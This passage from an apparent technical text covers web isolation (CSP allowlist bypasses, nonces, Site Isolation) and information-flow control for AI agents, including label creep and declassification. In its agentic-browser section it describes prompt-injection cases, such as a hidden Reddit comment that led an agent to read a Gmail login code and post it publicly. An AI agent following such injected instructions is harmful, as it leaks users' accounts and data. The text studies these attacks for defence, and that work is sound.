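The sites in the last row had restricted scripts to a list of approved hosts, but many still failed because a host on the list served something an attacker could use. Some hosts offered data through JSONP, an old technique that wraps the data in a call to a function that the requester names. An attacker could supply code in place of the name, and the browser would run the reply as a script from an approved host. Other hosts stored a copy of AngularJS, a library that finds and executes templates in a page, so an attacker could load the library and inject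 a template. Neither practice was a flaw until another site's policy trusted the host, so the hosts had no reason to change.

Of the 15 hosts that sites listed most often, 12 allowed a bypass outright and two more did if the policy also permitted `eval`. The researchers could bypass 94.8% of policies that listed 12 hosts, the median number. Roth, Barron and colleagues used the Internet Archive to follow 10,000 prominent sites and found that some lists contained misspelled or expired domain names, which an attacker could register.

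Weichselbaum and colleagues recommended nonces instead. A nonce is a random value that the server generates afresh for each page and puts in both the header and every script tag it writes itself. The browser runs only scripts with the right value. An injected tag has no nonce, so the browser won't run its script even if the tag points to a JSONP address on a trusted host. A nonce approves one script rather than everything on a host, much as a capability can grant access to one file rather than a whole directory. The `strict-dynamic` keyword also lets approved scripts load others, which many libraries need to do.

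Google Maps Activities, which had four million monthly users, switched from an allowlist to nonces with `strict-dynamic`. The allowlist needed five major changes during 2015, grew to 15 long paths and still included a JSONP address. After the switch, the policy needed no changes up to the time of the study. Nonces don't help if attackers can write inside an approved script or choose the address it loads another script from.

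Two recent surveys show how far sites have followed this advice. Web Almanac's *Security* covers 2025, and *Top 1 Million Analysis June 2026* (Helme, 2026) covers the 819,002 most popular sites that responded on 13 June.

| | Web Almanac | Helme |
|---|---|---|
| Sites with a policy | 21.9% | 20.8% |
| Basis of the shares below | policies with rules for scripts | all policies |
| `unsafe-inline` | 92% | 46.8% |
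| Nonces | about 20% | 24.7% |
| `strict-dynamic` | about 10% | 1.6% |

The figures for `unsafe-inline` differ so much largely because many policies don't regulate scripts at all. They may only prevent other sites from framing the page, for example, or switch its requests to HTTPS. Browsers also ignore `unsafe-inline` in some policies, including those that combine a nonce with `strict-dynamic`, so the 92% figure overstates the weakness. Nonces have become far more common since 2016, when fewer than 1% of the script rules in Weichselbaum and colleagues' collection used them.

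### One process for each site

Until 2018, Chrome often ran several sites in one operating-system process and relied on checks in its own code to keep them apart. An attacker's page could embed a bank's page in a frame and share a process with it. Spectre, an attack that uses timing to infer the contents of memory, made this unsafe because a script could read other data in its process even if the browser had no bugs.

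Browser makers first tried making clocks less precise and changing how they compiled JavaScript. Reis and colleagues found both approaches unsatisfactory. Attackers had other ways to measure time, and the compiler changes slowed some programs by up to 15% while missing some variants of the attack. Chrome adopted Site Isolation, which moves other sites' data out of a script's process, on the assumption that the script can read everything there. Each process handles one site, and a more trusted process withholds other sites' HTML and data files from it. A process can still load images and scripts from other sites, because pages have always been allowed to embed them.

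A site is larger than an origin because it consists of only the scheme and the registered domain, so `bank.example` and `pay.bank.example` belong to the same site. Chrome chose this coarser unit because pages could change their own origin to a parent domain while running, and up to 13.4% of page loads did so. Browsers have since deprecated that feature, and the Web Almanac found that under 0.5% of sites still used it.

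Adding Site Isolation to Chrome took almost 450,000 lines of code. The median number of page-rendering processes rose from 4.4 to 6.2, but each was smaller, so total memory use grew by only 9–13%. Pages took at most 2.25% longer to show their first content. Chrome turned Site Isolation on for desktop users in 2018. Chromium Blog's *Recent Site Isolation improvements* (2019) reports that Chrome turned it on for Android phones a year later, but only for sites where users enter passwords.

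### Why the crude policy spread

The same-origin policy is far less expressive than Jif's labels or even Flume's tags. It cannot label a document that combines data from two origins, and it does not control what a recipient does with data. Yet every major browser enforces it, while Jif and Flume remained research systems.

The same-origin policy succeeded largely because nobody has to write the labels. An address already contains the scheme, host and port, so the browser can label a page even if its author never thought about security. Jif programmers had to write many labels by hand. The default is also useful without changes, since most pages don't need to read each other's data. A site that needs an exception can add a CORS header for one address without the rest of the web having to adopt anything.

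CSP is a rough comparison, because it runs in the same browsers but requires each site to describe its own scripts. After more than a decade, about a fifth of sites have a policy. Report URI's *10 years of watching the web*, which draws on Helme's data, finds more broadly that protections hosting companies could switch on for their customers spread steadily, while those that needed continuing attention lagged. Report URI sells tools for managing CSP, so it has an interest in this conclusion, but the counts support it.

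The drawback of automatic labels is that the browser treats everything at one origin as equally trustworthy. A comment on Reddit has the same origin as the reader's Reddit account. Sites therefore remove scripts from users' posts, so that a comment is only text.

### An agent that reads every origin

An attacker can manipulate a browser agent with text alone, without running a script. These agents read pages, click and type on the user's behalf, usually in a browser where the user is already logged in. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (2026) argues that such agents undo three of the web's protections at once: the isolation of origins, the removal of scripts from user content, and the assumption that a person sees each page and performs each action.

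Chaikin and Kaul Sahib, in *Agentic Browser Security*, demonstrated the problem in August 2025 on Comet, a browser from the AI company Perplexity. They hid instructions in a Reddit comment and asked Comet to summarize the page. The agent looked up the user's email address on Perplexity's site, requested a login code, read the code in the user's open Gmail account and posted the address and code in a Reddit reply, which was enough to let an attacker take over the Perplexity account. The agent carried the data from one site to another, as a person with three tabs open could have done, without any script reading data from another origin.

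Chaikin and Kaul Sahib worked for Brave, which makes a competing browser. Perplexity shipped an incomplete fix within two days of their report. After publication, the two researchers found that a later fix had not fully stopped the attack either.

Other agentic browsers besides Comet were also vulnerable. Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven browsers in January and February 2026. In their attack, a malicious page embeds a page from another origin and instructs the agent to include the embedded page in any summary and enter that summary in a form. They used this attack to steal data through ChatGPT Atlas in agent mode. Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet also gave their agents enough access for the attack to work if an injection succeeded. The embedded page must allow framing, and the browser must send that page's cookies,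 which many browsers no longer do. But the attack also works in reverse, with a malicious advertisement using the agent to read the page around it.

The more restrictive products, including Brave's and Microsoft's, gave the model only limited information about a page, which also limited what the model could do. Brave, Google and Microsoft responded substantively to the findings. OpenAI declined the report because it lacked a complete injection attack, and Anthropic had not replied when the researchers published.

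An agent can also mix data from different origins without an attacker. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, describe a user who asks an agent to summarize a page and type the summary into a text box on that page. If the page contains a frame from another site, the summary may include the frame's contents, which the outer site then receives. The team tested five agentic browsers and six models, mostly on artificial pages, and found leaks both with and without attacks.

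### Limiting which origins an agent may use

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) sets out Google's response. For each task, Chrome is to keep two sets of origins. The agent may only read pages from the first set, but may read, click and type on pages from the second. Chrome withholds everything else from the model, including frames from unlisted origins inside a listed page. The model can propose new origins, but a separate gating function, which does not see web content, decides whether they are relevant. Chrome also prevents leaks through web addresses by allowing the model to write only addresses known to be public. It asks the user before visiting banking or medical sites, signing in with a saved password or completing a purchase.

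This automatically grants authority for one task, like a short list of capabilities in which each resource is an origin. It would have kept an agent asked to summarize a Reddit page from reaching Gmail. But the agent may send data from any readable origin to any writable one, so the sets limit the size of a leak without preventing leaks among the sites a task needs. The gate can also be wrong about which origins are relevant, particularly if an injected instruction influenced which ones the model proposed.

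The first version tracked only the origins the agent could act on, not those it could read. This is consistent with what Roesner and Kohlbrenner found in Chrome some weeks later.

Wang and colleagues instead track the data. Their system, SOPGuard, labels what the agent reads with its origin and passes the labels on to text the agent produces. When the agent is about to write to a page whose origin differs from the labels, SOPGuard pauses and asks the user for approval. In their tests it reduced unauthorized transfers to zero and added 2.07–5.79% to running time. Its weakness is its reliance on user approval. Many ordinary tasks move data between sites, such as copying a delivery address from an email into an order form, and a user who has approved many harmless transfers may well approve a harmful one.

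Labels are also harder to assign to instructions than to scripts. As *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out, a script normally comes from an explicit address, and a website's owner decides which scripts its pages include. An agent's instructions have no such address, and no owner has approved the ones it finds while working on a task.

*Prismata* (2026) divides pages more finely than by origin. It labels parts of a page by who supplied them, such as the site's developer, its users or an outside party. A separate model, given only the user's task, selects the kinds of content the task requires. Cancelling a subscription, for instance, shouldn't require reading other users' comments. Ordinary code then removes all other content before the agent sees the page, and makes some of the remaining content read-only.

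*SPIDES* (2026) comes closer to the decentralized label model. It labels each page element with a trust level and a set of readers, which can include the user and website origins. For example, a private document on one site has the label (Trusted, {user, that site}). The agent starts without seeing any untrusted or restricted content, but can pass it to an isolated model. If the agent asks to see the content itself, its context takes on the content's label. For the evaluation, the researchers marked up page elements on 16 of 28 origins themselves, which brings back the labelling work that the same-origin policy avoided.

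Suppose Ana's assistant uses her webmail at `https://mail.example` and a courier's site to book a delivery. Origin sets would keep the assistant away from her bank, whatever instructions the stranger's message contains. They would not separate that message from Ben's contract, because both come from `mail.example`. If the task also includes answering mail, the assistant needs write access to `mail.example`, and the stranger can again try to get the contract forwarded. To protect one message from another, Ana still needs the reply capability for Ben's thread, or labels that record who sent each message.

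## Keeping labels from accumulating: label creep and label explosion

Labels that record who sent each message distinguish Ben's contract from the stranger's text only until the assistant reads both. After that, everything the assistant writes carries the join of the two labels, and each further message it reads either leaves that label unchanged or raises it.

Sabelfeld and Myers (2003), in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, call this steady rise label creep and explain why a run-time monitor can't simply undo it. Lowering a process's label after a branch on a secret would be unsafe, because a variable that the program left unchanged may reveal the secret, as y did in the four-line program. The labels on stored data rise too, because a variable that receives a new value must keep the higher of the old and new labels. Sabelfeld and Myers judged run-time labelling too restrictive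 for general use, citing Denning's 1982 textbook.

*APPA* (2026), which presents an information-flow system for agents, proves that an agent's label can change only a limited number of times. Each label consists of a set of permitted readers and a trust level. When an agent takes in a message, its new label keeps only the readers allowed by both its old label and the message's label, and takes the lower of the two trust levels. With five possible readers and two trust levels, the label can change at most six times before it reaches the top of Denning's lattice, where nobody may read the agent's output and the output is untrusted. A context or memory that keeps absorbing data from varied sources tends to end up there.

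Label explosion is this end state, in which nearly everything carries the labels of nearly everything else. Authors use the two terms loosely. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* uses "label explosion" in this sense, but *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions* (Stefan, Russo and colleagues) defines label creep itself as the point where a computation can no longer do anything useful. Some authors also use "explosion" for uncontrolled growth in the number of distinct labels, which slows a system down but doesn't make its labels more restrictive.

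### How quickly a context fills up

If each tool result independently has a 10% chance of being secret, a context containing 20 results has a 0.9²⁰, or about 12%, chance of still being unrestricted.

| Results absorbed | Still unrestricted if 10% are secret | Still unrestricted if 1% are secret |
|---|---|---|
| 5 | 59% | 95% |
| 20 | 12% | 82% |
| 50 | 0.5% | 61% |

Real results are not independent, and an agent may spend a morning reading public web pages without encountering any secrets. Label creep is usually worse for integrity, because every web page and stranger's email counts as untrusted, and reading just one is enough to bar the agent from making payments.

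Label creep also depends on which flows are tracked. Staicu and colleagues measured creep in their JavaScript programs as the share of assignments that stored a sensitive value, and found that tracking implicit flows raised it by over 40%. The share peaked at only about 20% on average, but their policies marked only the few sources involved in known flaws, far fewer than an agent has when it labels everything it reads.

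Label creep causes refusals that seem arbitrary to users, because the cause is something the program read earlier. In an example from Stefan and colleagues, Alice asks conference-reviewing software for a list of her own submissions. If the software reads Bob's paper while compiling the list, it can no longer reply to Alice. Similarly, Ana's assistant might read the contract in the morning and then refuse to look up a train in the afternoon.

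A designer can replace the refusals with requests for approval, but at the 10% rate, an assistant with 20 results in its context would have to ask about public actions 88% of the time. Nearly all of those actions would be harmless, so Ana would probably stop reading the requests or permanently allow all web searches, including any that contained the contract's terms.

### The classical remedies and their prices

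Labelling smaller pieces of data slows label creep. Jif labels each variable, so a program can read the contract into one variable without changing the labels on the others. Stefan and colleagues object that programmers then have to think about labels on values that don't matter, and usually need a new language or run-time system. Their own system, LIO, instead lets a program hold individual values in sealed wrappers, each with its own label, and check the label before opening the wrapper. The conference software can therefore pick out the papers Alice may see, open only those and reply to her.

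This doesn't work inside a language model, because every input can affect the output. The basic design in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) therefore gives each response the join of the labels on all messages so far. The paper describes this approach as sound but possibly too conservative.

Separate contexts are another remedy. Asbestos's event processes kept each user's labels apart, and an agent can likewise start each task with an empty context. If Ana's 20 results are spread over four contexts of five, each context has a 59% chance of staying unrestricted. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* illustrates the drawback with a user who asks an agent to comment on a software issue and then to summarize the same issue. Clearing the context between the two tasks is secure, but the agent loses what it learned from the first.

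Scoped computation, as in LIO's `toLabeled`, confines the rise to one block of code and returns the result in a sealed wrapper. *Language-Based Agent Control* applies this to a call from one agent to another. In simplified form:

```
summary <- toLabeled Confidential (agent "Summarize Ben's contract")
fetch "http://trains.example"      -- still allowed
text <- unlabel summary            -- the main agent's label rises here
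```

The main agent can pass the sealed summary to the tool that replies to Ben without opening it. But if the agent needs the contents to decide what to do next, it has to open the summary, which raises its label. Programmers also have to notice which code needs a block. In the conference software, a function that changes only a paper's abstract first reads the whole paper, which raises the label for everything that runs afterwards.

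A clearance sets a task's maximum label in advance. If a worker with Public clearance tries to open the contract, LIO reports an error. The program can catch the error and continue its public work, so an unplanned read can't spoil the rest of the task. However, someone has to predict what each task needs to read, and a task that needs both the contract and the web still fails.

Precise static analysis avoids some of the creep altogether. The statement after an `if` runs whichever branch the program took, so reaching it reveals nothing about the secret (provided that both branches finish). A static checker can therefore restore the earlier program-counter label, because it has examined both branches. *SPA* (2026) uses this kind of check on an agent's plan before the plan runs:

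```
contract := read(message from Ben)          # Confidential
summary  := model("summarize", contract)    # Confidential
trains   := fetch("http://trains.example")  # Public
```

The web request passes even though an earlier step of the plan read the contract, because nothing from the contract affects the request. But the model has to write the plan before it sees the contract, so it can't adapt later steps to the contract's contents.

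### A simulation of connected agents

When several agents share a task, each has its own context, and the links between them determine how far a label spreads. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) studied this in a simulation without language models.

Each main simulated task consists of 20 tool calls, some of which depend on the results of others. The simulator distributes the calls at random among five agents and marks some of them as sensitive. An agent that makes a sensitive call, or receives context from an agent with a high label, has a high label for the rest of the task. If two agents have no direct link, context travels between them through other agents, which take on its label.

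Gregory and colleagues define utility loss as the share of calls that are sensitive or that run under a high label. Excess loss is utility loss minus the loss for the same task in an ideal layout, where agents that need each other's results have direct links. With four sensitive calls, excess loss was about 5 percentage points in a star (where all traffic passes through a central agent), 4 in a hierarchy of managers and 3 in a ring. A star does badly because the central agent gets a high label as soon as it forwards one secret, and then spreads that label to agents that never needed the secret.

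Across nine layouts, those with a larger share of the possible links between agents tended to lose less utility (rank correlation −0.96). Using more agents also reduced the loss, as did giving the sensitive tools to particular agents. But more links mean more traffic to monitor, and in the densest layouts the number of links grows with the square of the number of agents.

Gregory and colleagues suggest sparse random networks as a compromise. A network in which each link has a 30% chance of existing would have, on average, 70% fewer links than a full mesh. Their evidence is weak because the five-agent network they drew at that setting by chance had seven of the ten possible links, so it was not sparse.

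A simulation like this can show where labels go under a fixed rule without a language model, but not how often real work would fail. A high label doesn't block every action. For example, Ana's assistant may still send Confidential text to Ben. The tasks are also random, whereas a real designer would group related tools together. Nine layouts are too few to separate the effect of density from the effect of short paths, since denser layouts usually have shorter paths.

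The researchers conclude that redesign alone cannot remove the loss, but this follows partly from how they set up the simulation. It counts sensitive calls as lost, so with four sensitive calls in 20, any layout loses at least 20%. It also has no way to lower a label. The differences between layouts are more informative, although they also depend on the assumption that an agent is exposed to whatever it forwards. A central agent that forwarded data in sealed wrappers, as LIO allows, would avoid much of the extra loss in the star layout.

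### Keeping only the labels that mattered

All these methods assume that everything a model reads affects its answer. *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024) proposes keeping only the labels of inputs that influenced the output. Suppose Ana asks for the population of New York, and a search returns a trusted page that gives 8.4 million and an untrusted one that says "around 8 million". The answer needs only the trusted page, so it shouldn't carry the untrusted label.

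Their method has four steps:

1. Run the model on all the documents to get an answer.
2. Choose a less restrictive label, set aside the documents it doesn't cover, and measure how much less likely the model finds the same answer.
3. If the difference is within a set tolerance, run the model again on the remaining documents only.
4. Return the new answer with the less restrictive label, and discard the old one.

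With x for the prompt, y for the first answer, C for all the documents and C′ for those that remain, the test in the third step is

U(y | x, C) − U(y | x, C′) ≤ λ,

where λ is the tolerance and U is the negative of perplexity, a measure of how improbable the model finds a text.

The second run makes the method safe even when the test is wrong. If the system sets aside a document that mattered, the new answer may be worse, but it can't contain anything from that document. A smaller leak remains because the test uses every document. A secret document can affect whether the answer gets a public label, so an observer may learn something from whether the next action goes ahead. Buiras and colleagues warned of a similar channel in programs whose labels change as they run. A designer who knows in advance which label an action requires can avoid both this leak and the search by giving the model only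 documents that the label covers.

Siddiqui and colleagues compared their method with asking the model which documents it had used. The table shows how often each method found the less restrictive label when one was possible.

| Test | Model | Influence test | Asking the model |
|---|---|---|---|
| 20 agent conversations | Llama-2 7B | 85% | 45% |
| 20 agent conversations | Llama-2 70B | 95% | 80% |
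| 647 questions about news articles | Llama-2 7B | 57% | not reported |
| 647 questions about news articles | Llama-2 70B | 39% | not reported |

These tests were small and used models that are now old, and the researchers wrote the agent conversations themselves. The gap between the methods was much smaller with the larger model. Since the safety comes from the second run, a designer could let a strong model choose the documents and still rerun it on those alone. The possible gain from any such method is also limited. In the news test, only 647 of the 3,465 questions allowed a less restrictive label, and the restrictive label was correct for the rest.

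The amount of computation depends on the number of labels. With two levels, the method needs one comparison and one extra run. In a test where 14 documents each had their own label, there were 16,384 possible combinations of labels, although the search normally skips most of them.

An attacker can't use the method to give untrusted text a trusted label, but can prevent it from relaxing a restrictive label. If the attacker adds distracting text that changes the model's first answer, the trusted documents alone no longer support that answer, and the system keeps the restrictive label. Siddiqui and colleagues acknowledge this weakness. For Ana, it brings back the problem with Biba's low-water-mark policy, under which any stranger could block her payments by sending a message.

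*GIF* (2026) instead estimates influence from how the model's output responds to small changes in each part of its input. In one example, an address in a user's private notes had no effect on the output. *GIF* assigned it zero flow, while a method based on the model's attention assigned it 9%. *GIF*'s guarantee covers only changes close to the actual input. Because *GIF* measures the flow in an existing answer instead of producing a new one from fewer documents, its safety depends on the measurement being right.

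None of this helps when the answer depends on the restricted data. If Ben asks about his penalty clause, the assistant has to use the contract, and the reply should carry the contract's label, which allows it to go to Ben. If Ana wants to send the same explanation to her accountant, Carla, someone with the authority to declassify it has to deliberately lower its secrecy.

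## Releasing information deliberately: declassification and endorsement

Declassification deliberately lowers the secrecy of data. Endorsement, its counterpart for integrity, deliberately raises the trust placed in data so that it may influence protected actions. Label creep makes both necessary, but even a system with perfectly precise labels would need them, because noninterference forbids many useful programs.

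A cash machine that rejects the PIN 4821 reveals that the PIN is not 4821. Its output depends on a secret, so noninterference forbids the check just as it forbids a program that prints the PIN. Yet the two reveal very different amounts. If all 10,000 PINs are equally likely, the PIN contains log₂ 10,000 ≈ 13.3 bits of information. A random guess is right with probability p = 1/10,000, and the machine's answer reveals on average

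p log₂(1/p) + (1 − p) log₂(1/(1 − p)) ≈ 0.0015 bits.

Someone who can try 10,000 different guesses still learns the whole PIN. If the machine keeps the card after three wrong guesses, a thief learns an average of about 0.0044 bits. The limit on guesses protects the PIN as much as how little each answer reveals.

### What, who, where and when

Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, classify release policies by what information a program releases, who controls the release, where in the system it happens and when. A policy that covers only one of these leaves a way round it:

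| Dimension | Example policy | A way round it |
|---|---|---|
| What | A shop's log may include four digits of a card number. | An attacker makes several purchases and asks for different digits each time. |
| Who | Only code with the owner's authority may release information about a password. | That code releases the password itself instead of the result of checking a guess. |
| Where | Secrets may leave only through one marked line of code. | An earlier line copies another secret into the variable that the marked line releases. |
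| When | A software key stays secret until the customer has paid. | After the payment, the program sends out other secrets too. |

Owner-based release in Jif covers only the "who" dimension. *Decentralized Delimited Release* points out that Jif does not distinguish a program that reveals whether a guess matches a password from one that reveals the password itself. JSFlow, a JavaScript interpreter that tracks labels, covers only the "where" dimension. *Prudent Design Principles for Information Flow Control* (Bastys, Piessens and Sabelfeld, 2018) shows that JSFlow accepts both `declassify(guess == pwd)` and `declassify(pwd)`.

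Sabelfeld and Sands compare the four dimensions to the perimeter of a network, which is only as secure as its weakest point. They also propose principles for testing any definition of secure release:

- *Semantic consistency:* replacing code that releases nothing with equivalent code does not change whether the program counts as secure.
- *Conservativity:* for programs without declassification, the definition is equivalent to noninterference.
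- *Monotonicity of release:* adding a declassification cannot make a secure program insecure.
- *Non-occlusion:* a declassification cannot hide another leak.

The last principle matters because a definition of security can satisfy the first three and still allow serious leaks. One such definition calls a program secure if any two runs either look the same to the public or include a declassification. Under this definition, a program could declassify a harmless constant, then publish every secret it holds, and still count as secure.

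Published definitions also fail some of these tests. One by Mantel and Sands assumes that an attacker can see when a declassification happens. Under that definition, marking a harmless assignment as a declassification can make a secure program count as insecure if the assignment is in only one branch of a conditional that depends on a secret. Sabelfeld and Sands treat such failures as warnings that need an explanation, because some policies fail a test for good reasons.

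### Delimited release

Sabelfeld and Myers, in *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, address the "what" dimension. The programmer marks the expressions that a program may release, which they call escape hatches. Let M₁ and M₂ be two possible contents of memory at the start of a run. The program satisfies delimited release if, for every such pair:

if M₁ and M₂ agree on all public variables and on the value of every escape hatch, then the runs from M₁ and M₂ give the same public results.

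Suppose a company wants to publish the average of two salaries, `h1` and `h2`:

```
avg := declassify((h1 + h2) / 2)     # secure

h2 := h1
avg := declassify((h1 + h2) / 2)     # insecure
```

Suppose the two salaries are €2,000 and €3,000 in one run and swapped in the other. The average is €2,500 in both runs, so the public result must be the same. The first program passes, but the second fails because it publishes €2,000 in one run and €3,000 in the other. This is a laundering attack, which sends a secret out through a release meant for something else. A reviewer who read only the `declassify` lines would miss it, because those lines are identical in both programs.

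An attack on an electronic wallet shows how much a small release can leak. The wallet is allowed to reveal whether it holds enough money for an item. A malicious program checks whether the balance is at least 2ⁿ⁻¹, subtracts that amount if so, and repeats this with each smaller power of two. After n checks it has the whole n-bit balance. Delimited release rules this out because it evaluates the escape hatch on the values at the start of the run, which permits releasing the result of only one check.

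A compiler can enforce delimited release by rejecting any program that changes a variable before declassifying an expression that contains it. This rule also rejects some secure programs, such as one that replaces a secret number with its parity (odd or even) and then declassifies the result.

The definition covers only a single run, so it does not stop someone from running a PIN checker 10,000 times. It cannot express "release either of these secrets, but not both". It also ignores how hard it is to work out a secret from the released information. If a program may release a scrambled version of a password, and no other password has the same scrambled version, the definition also lets the program publish the password itself.

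Sabelfeld and Sands found that delimited release fails non-occlusion as well:

```
if true then l := h * h
else l := declassify(h * h)
```

The marked release never runs, but its presence makes the unmarked one acceptable. *Localized Delimited Release*, by Askarov and Sabelfeld, therefore combines "what" with "where", and *Decentralized Delimited Release* combines "what" with ownership.

### Robust declassification

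Zdancewic and Myers introduced robust declassification in 2001 to deal with attackers who manipulate a release. Under this property, an attacker may see what a system releases but must not be able to affect what it releases or whether it releases anything. In *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic later defined the property for a programming language and showed how a compiler can enforce it.

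They represent a program as trusted code with holes that an attacker can fill. The attacker's code may change untrusted variables but may not declassify anything itself. Let c[a] be the program with its holes filled by attack a. Leaving aside runs that never finish, the program is robust if, for all attacks a and a′ and all starting memories M₁ and M₂:

if the attacker cannot tell M₁ from M₂ by running c[a], the attacker cannot tell them apart by running c[a′] either.

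An attacker who interferes therefore learns no more than one who only watches. A designer can check that the releases are acceptable when nobody interferes, without considering every possible attack.

The compiler accepts `v := declassify(e)` only if three conditions hold:

- All the data in `e` is trusted.
- The program-counter label is trusted, so no untrusted data has influenced whether the program reached this line.
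- The variable `v` may hold data with the new, lower label.

This program fails the second condition if `x` is untrusted:

```
[attacker's code]
if x then y := declassify(z)
```

The attacker can learn the value of `z` by setting `x` to true, but learns nothing about `z` if `x` is false. Making `x` a trusted variable, which the attacker's code cannot change, fixes this. The program can still release `z`, but only trusted code controls whether it does.

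An earlier type system by Zdancewic lacked the first condition and accepted this program:

```
if x then y := secret1 else y := secret2     # x is untrusted
w := declassify(y)
```

The release always happens, but the attacker chooses which secret it contains. Under the newer rule, `y` becomes untrusted because `x` influenced it, so the compiler rejects the release.

Robustness does not limit the amount of information released. A program that always publishes all its secrets is robust, because no attack can make it reveal more.

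### Endorsement and its risks

Some programs have to let an outsider influence what information they release. In Battleship, players hide ships on a grid and take turns naming a square to learn whether it contains a ship. The opponent's choice of square determines what the program reveals, so the game violates robustness.

Endorsement allows such exceptions. The program endorses the opponent's move and then uses it as trusted data. Myers and colleagues allow an endorsement only where the program-counter label is trusted, so an attacker cannot decide whether it happens. Under the resulting guarantee, which they call qualified robustness, an endorsed value could be anything, and an attacker's influence through it is no longer a violation. The surrounding code must therefore be safe for every possible move. If it accepted "all squares" as a move, the opponent could see the whole board without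 violating qualified robustness.

Qualified robustness also fails non-occlusion. Suppose an endorsed value is always 0 or 1, and the program releases a secret if the value exceeds 42, which can never happen. But the definition treats 43 as a possible value, so it counts this release as possible and fails to detect that the attacker controls a later release of the same secret. The compiler's rules reject this program even though the definition accepts it. *Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity* (Askarov and Myers, 2011) still described defining what such systems guarantee as a continuing challenge.

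A PIN checker needs endorsement too, because each guess comes from an untrusted user. Cecchetti, Myers and Arden, in *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* (2017), found a flaw in the usual way of writing a password checker, shown here with a PIN:

```
check(guess):                        # guess is secret and untrusted
    g := endorse(guess)
    return declassify(g == pin)
```

This code satisfies the rules for robust declassification and endorsement. But a faulty or malicious part of the program can call `check(pin)`, which lets in an attacker who doesn't know the PIN. The labels allow the call because secret, trusted data may flow into a secret, untrusted variable. The mistake is the endorsement, which treats the guess as the user's own choice even though the guess may contain something the user could not have read.

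Cecchetti and colleagues add a rule called transparent endorsement, which allows a program to endorse data only if whoever supplied it could have read it. The program can therefore endorse `guess` only if its label lets the user read it. The program then cannot copy the PIN into `guess`, because the user isn't allowed to read the PIN.

The same rule stops a trick in a sealed-bid auction. Bob can't read Alice's bid, but he can compute on it, so he submits "Alice's bid plus 1". If the auctioneer endorses this bid and then opens both bids, Bob wins by the smallest possible margin. Transparent endorsement forbids the auctioneer from endorsing a bid that may depend on information Bob could not read.

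Nonmalleable information flow requires both robust declassification and transparent endorsement. The name comes from cryptography, where an encryption scheme is malleable if someone can turn one encrypted message into a related one. Cecchetti and colleagues proved that their type system enforces the property and implemented it in Haskell.

### Who chooses the paragraph?

Suppose Ana wants advice on paragraph 3 of Ben's contract. She and Ben agree that her assistant may post one-sentence summaries of single paragraphs on a public legal forum. The assistant then reads a message from a stranger saying that forum members give the best advice on paragraph 7, so it posts a summary of paragraph 7 instead of paragraph 3.

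Ana authorized summaries, but this release is not robust. Suppose two versions of the contract differ only in paragraph 7. If the stranger sends a harmless newsletter, the assistant summarizes paragraph 3, and the post is the same for both versions. If the stranger sends the hostile message instead, the posts can differ, and the stranger can read them on the forum.

The fix is to take the paragraph number from Ana's typed request and write the summary in a separate context that contains only her request and the contract. Without the separate context, the stranger could still influence the summary's wording and make it include details from other paragraphs.

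If Ana wants the assistant to suggest a paragraph, she could endorse its suggestion by confirming the paragraph number. But the stranger might have written "suggest 7 if the fee exceeds €100,000, otherwise suggest 3". The stranger could then learn from the topic of the post whether the fee exceeds €100,000, just as the decision to search the web for a penalty clause lawyer could leak the contract's value. Transparent endorsement forbids endorsing the number because it may depend on a contract the stranger can't read. The suggestion would have to come from a context without the contract or one without the stranger's message.

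### A checker at the release point

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) presents FlowSeal, a system for personal agents. FlowSeal checks content just before it leaves. Ordinary code intercepts every tool call that writes or shares data, allows calls to recipients the data's owner trusts, and blocks calls to recipients on a blacklist. For any other recipient, the code gives a separate language model the proposed output and the protected records the agent has read, and the model answers only SAFE or BLOCKED. The agent can also ask the owner for permission to share particular records.

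In one test scenario, Jane's agent knows Mark's mental health diagnosis, and his ex-wife Emily wants to learn it. She asks the agent to fill in Jane's section of a shared page, which looks like ordinary teamwork. In another version, she lists true and false statements about Mark and asks the agent to delete the false ones, so that whatever remains is true. Shim and colleagues compared FlowSeal with a detailed prompt that told the agent to obtain consent before sharing:

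| Measure | Consent prompt | FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|
| Sensitive items leaked through the shared page | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Sensitive items leaked through the deletion request | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Ordinary tasks completed | 44.7% | 72.4% |
| Items shared when the owner was willing to consent | 66.6% | 32.7% |

A simpler prompt did slightly better than FlowSeal on ordinary tasks, at 75.9%, but leaked 31.8% of the items through the shared page. FlowSeal's main drawback, shown in the last row of the table, is that it often failed to make releases the owner would have approved. Shim and colleagues attribute this to the agent asking for consent less often.

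The checker is essential. Replacing it with one that approved everything raised leaks through the shared page to 24.9%. A checker that blocked everything kept leaks at 1.3%, but the agent completed no ordinary tasks.

FlowSeal covers "what" by comparing the output with the protected records, "who" by asking their owner, and "where" by intercepting every outgoing call. It covers "when" only partly. It requires consent before a protected record is released, but its checker judges each output separately. Shim and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker could split a fact across several messages that each look harmless, much as the thief learns a PIN from many small answers.

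FlowSeal also does not make releases robust. A requester can influence which records the agent asks to share, and the design leaves prompt injection out of scope. FlowSeal's formal guarantee holds only if the checker never wrongly answers SAFE. The checker is a language model that reads text an attacker may have influenced, so an instruction in that text might mislead it.

### What to write down for each release point

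For every place where a system lowers a label, the designer should record the four dimensions, who can influence the release, and any endorsements it depends on. For Ana's forum posts, the record might look like this:

| Question | Ana's forum posts |
|---|---|
| What may leave, and what is it computed from? | One sentence of at most 200 characters, computed from one paragraph of the contract |
| Who receives it? | Anyone |
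| Who must consent? | Ana and Ben |
| Where does the release happen? | In one function, the only code that can remove the contract's label for a post |
| When, and how often? | After Ana approves the text, and at most three times per contract |
| Who may influence the choice and the wording? | Ana, through her typed request, and Ben, through the contract |
| Which untrusted data does it endorse, and why? | None |
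| What is the most it can reveal? | 600 characters, plus the timing and number of the posts |

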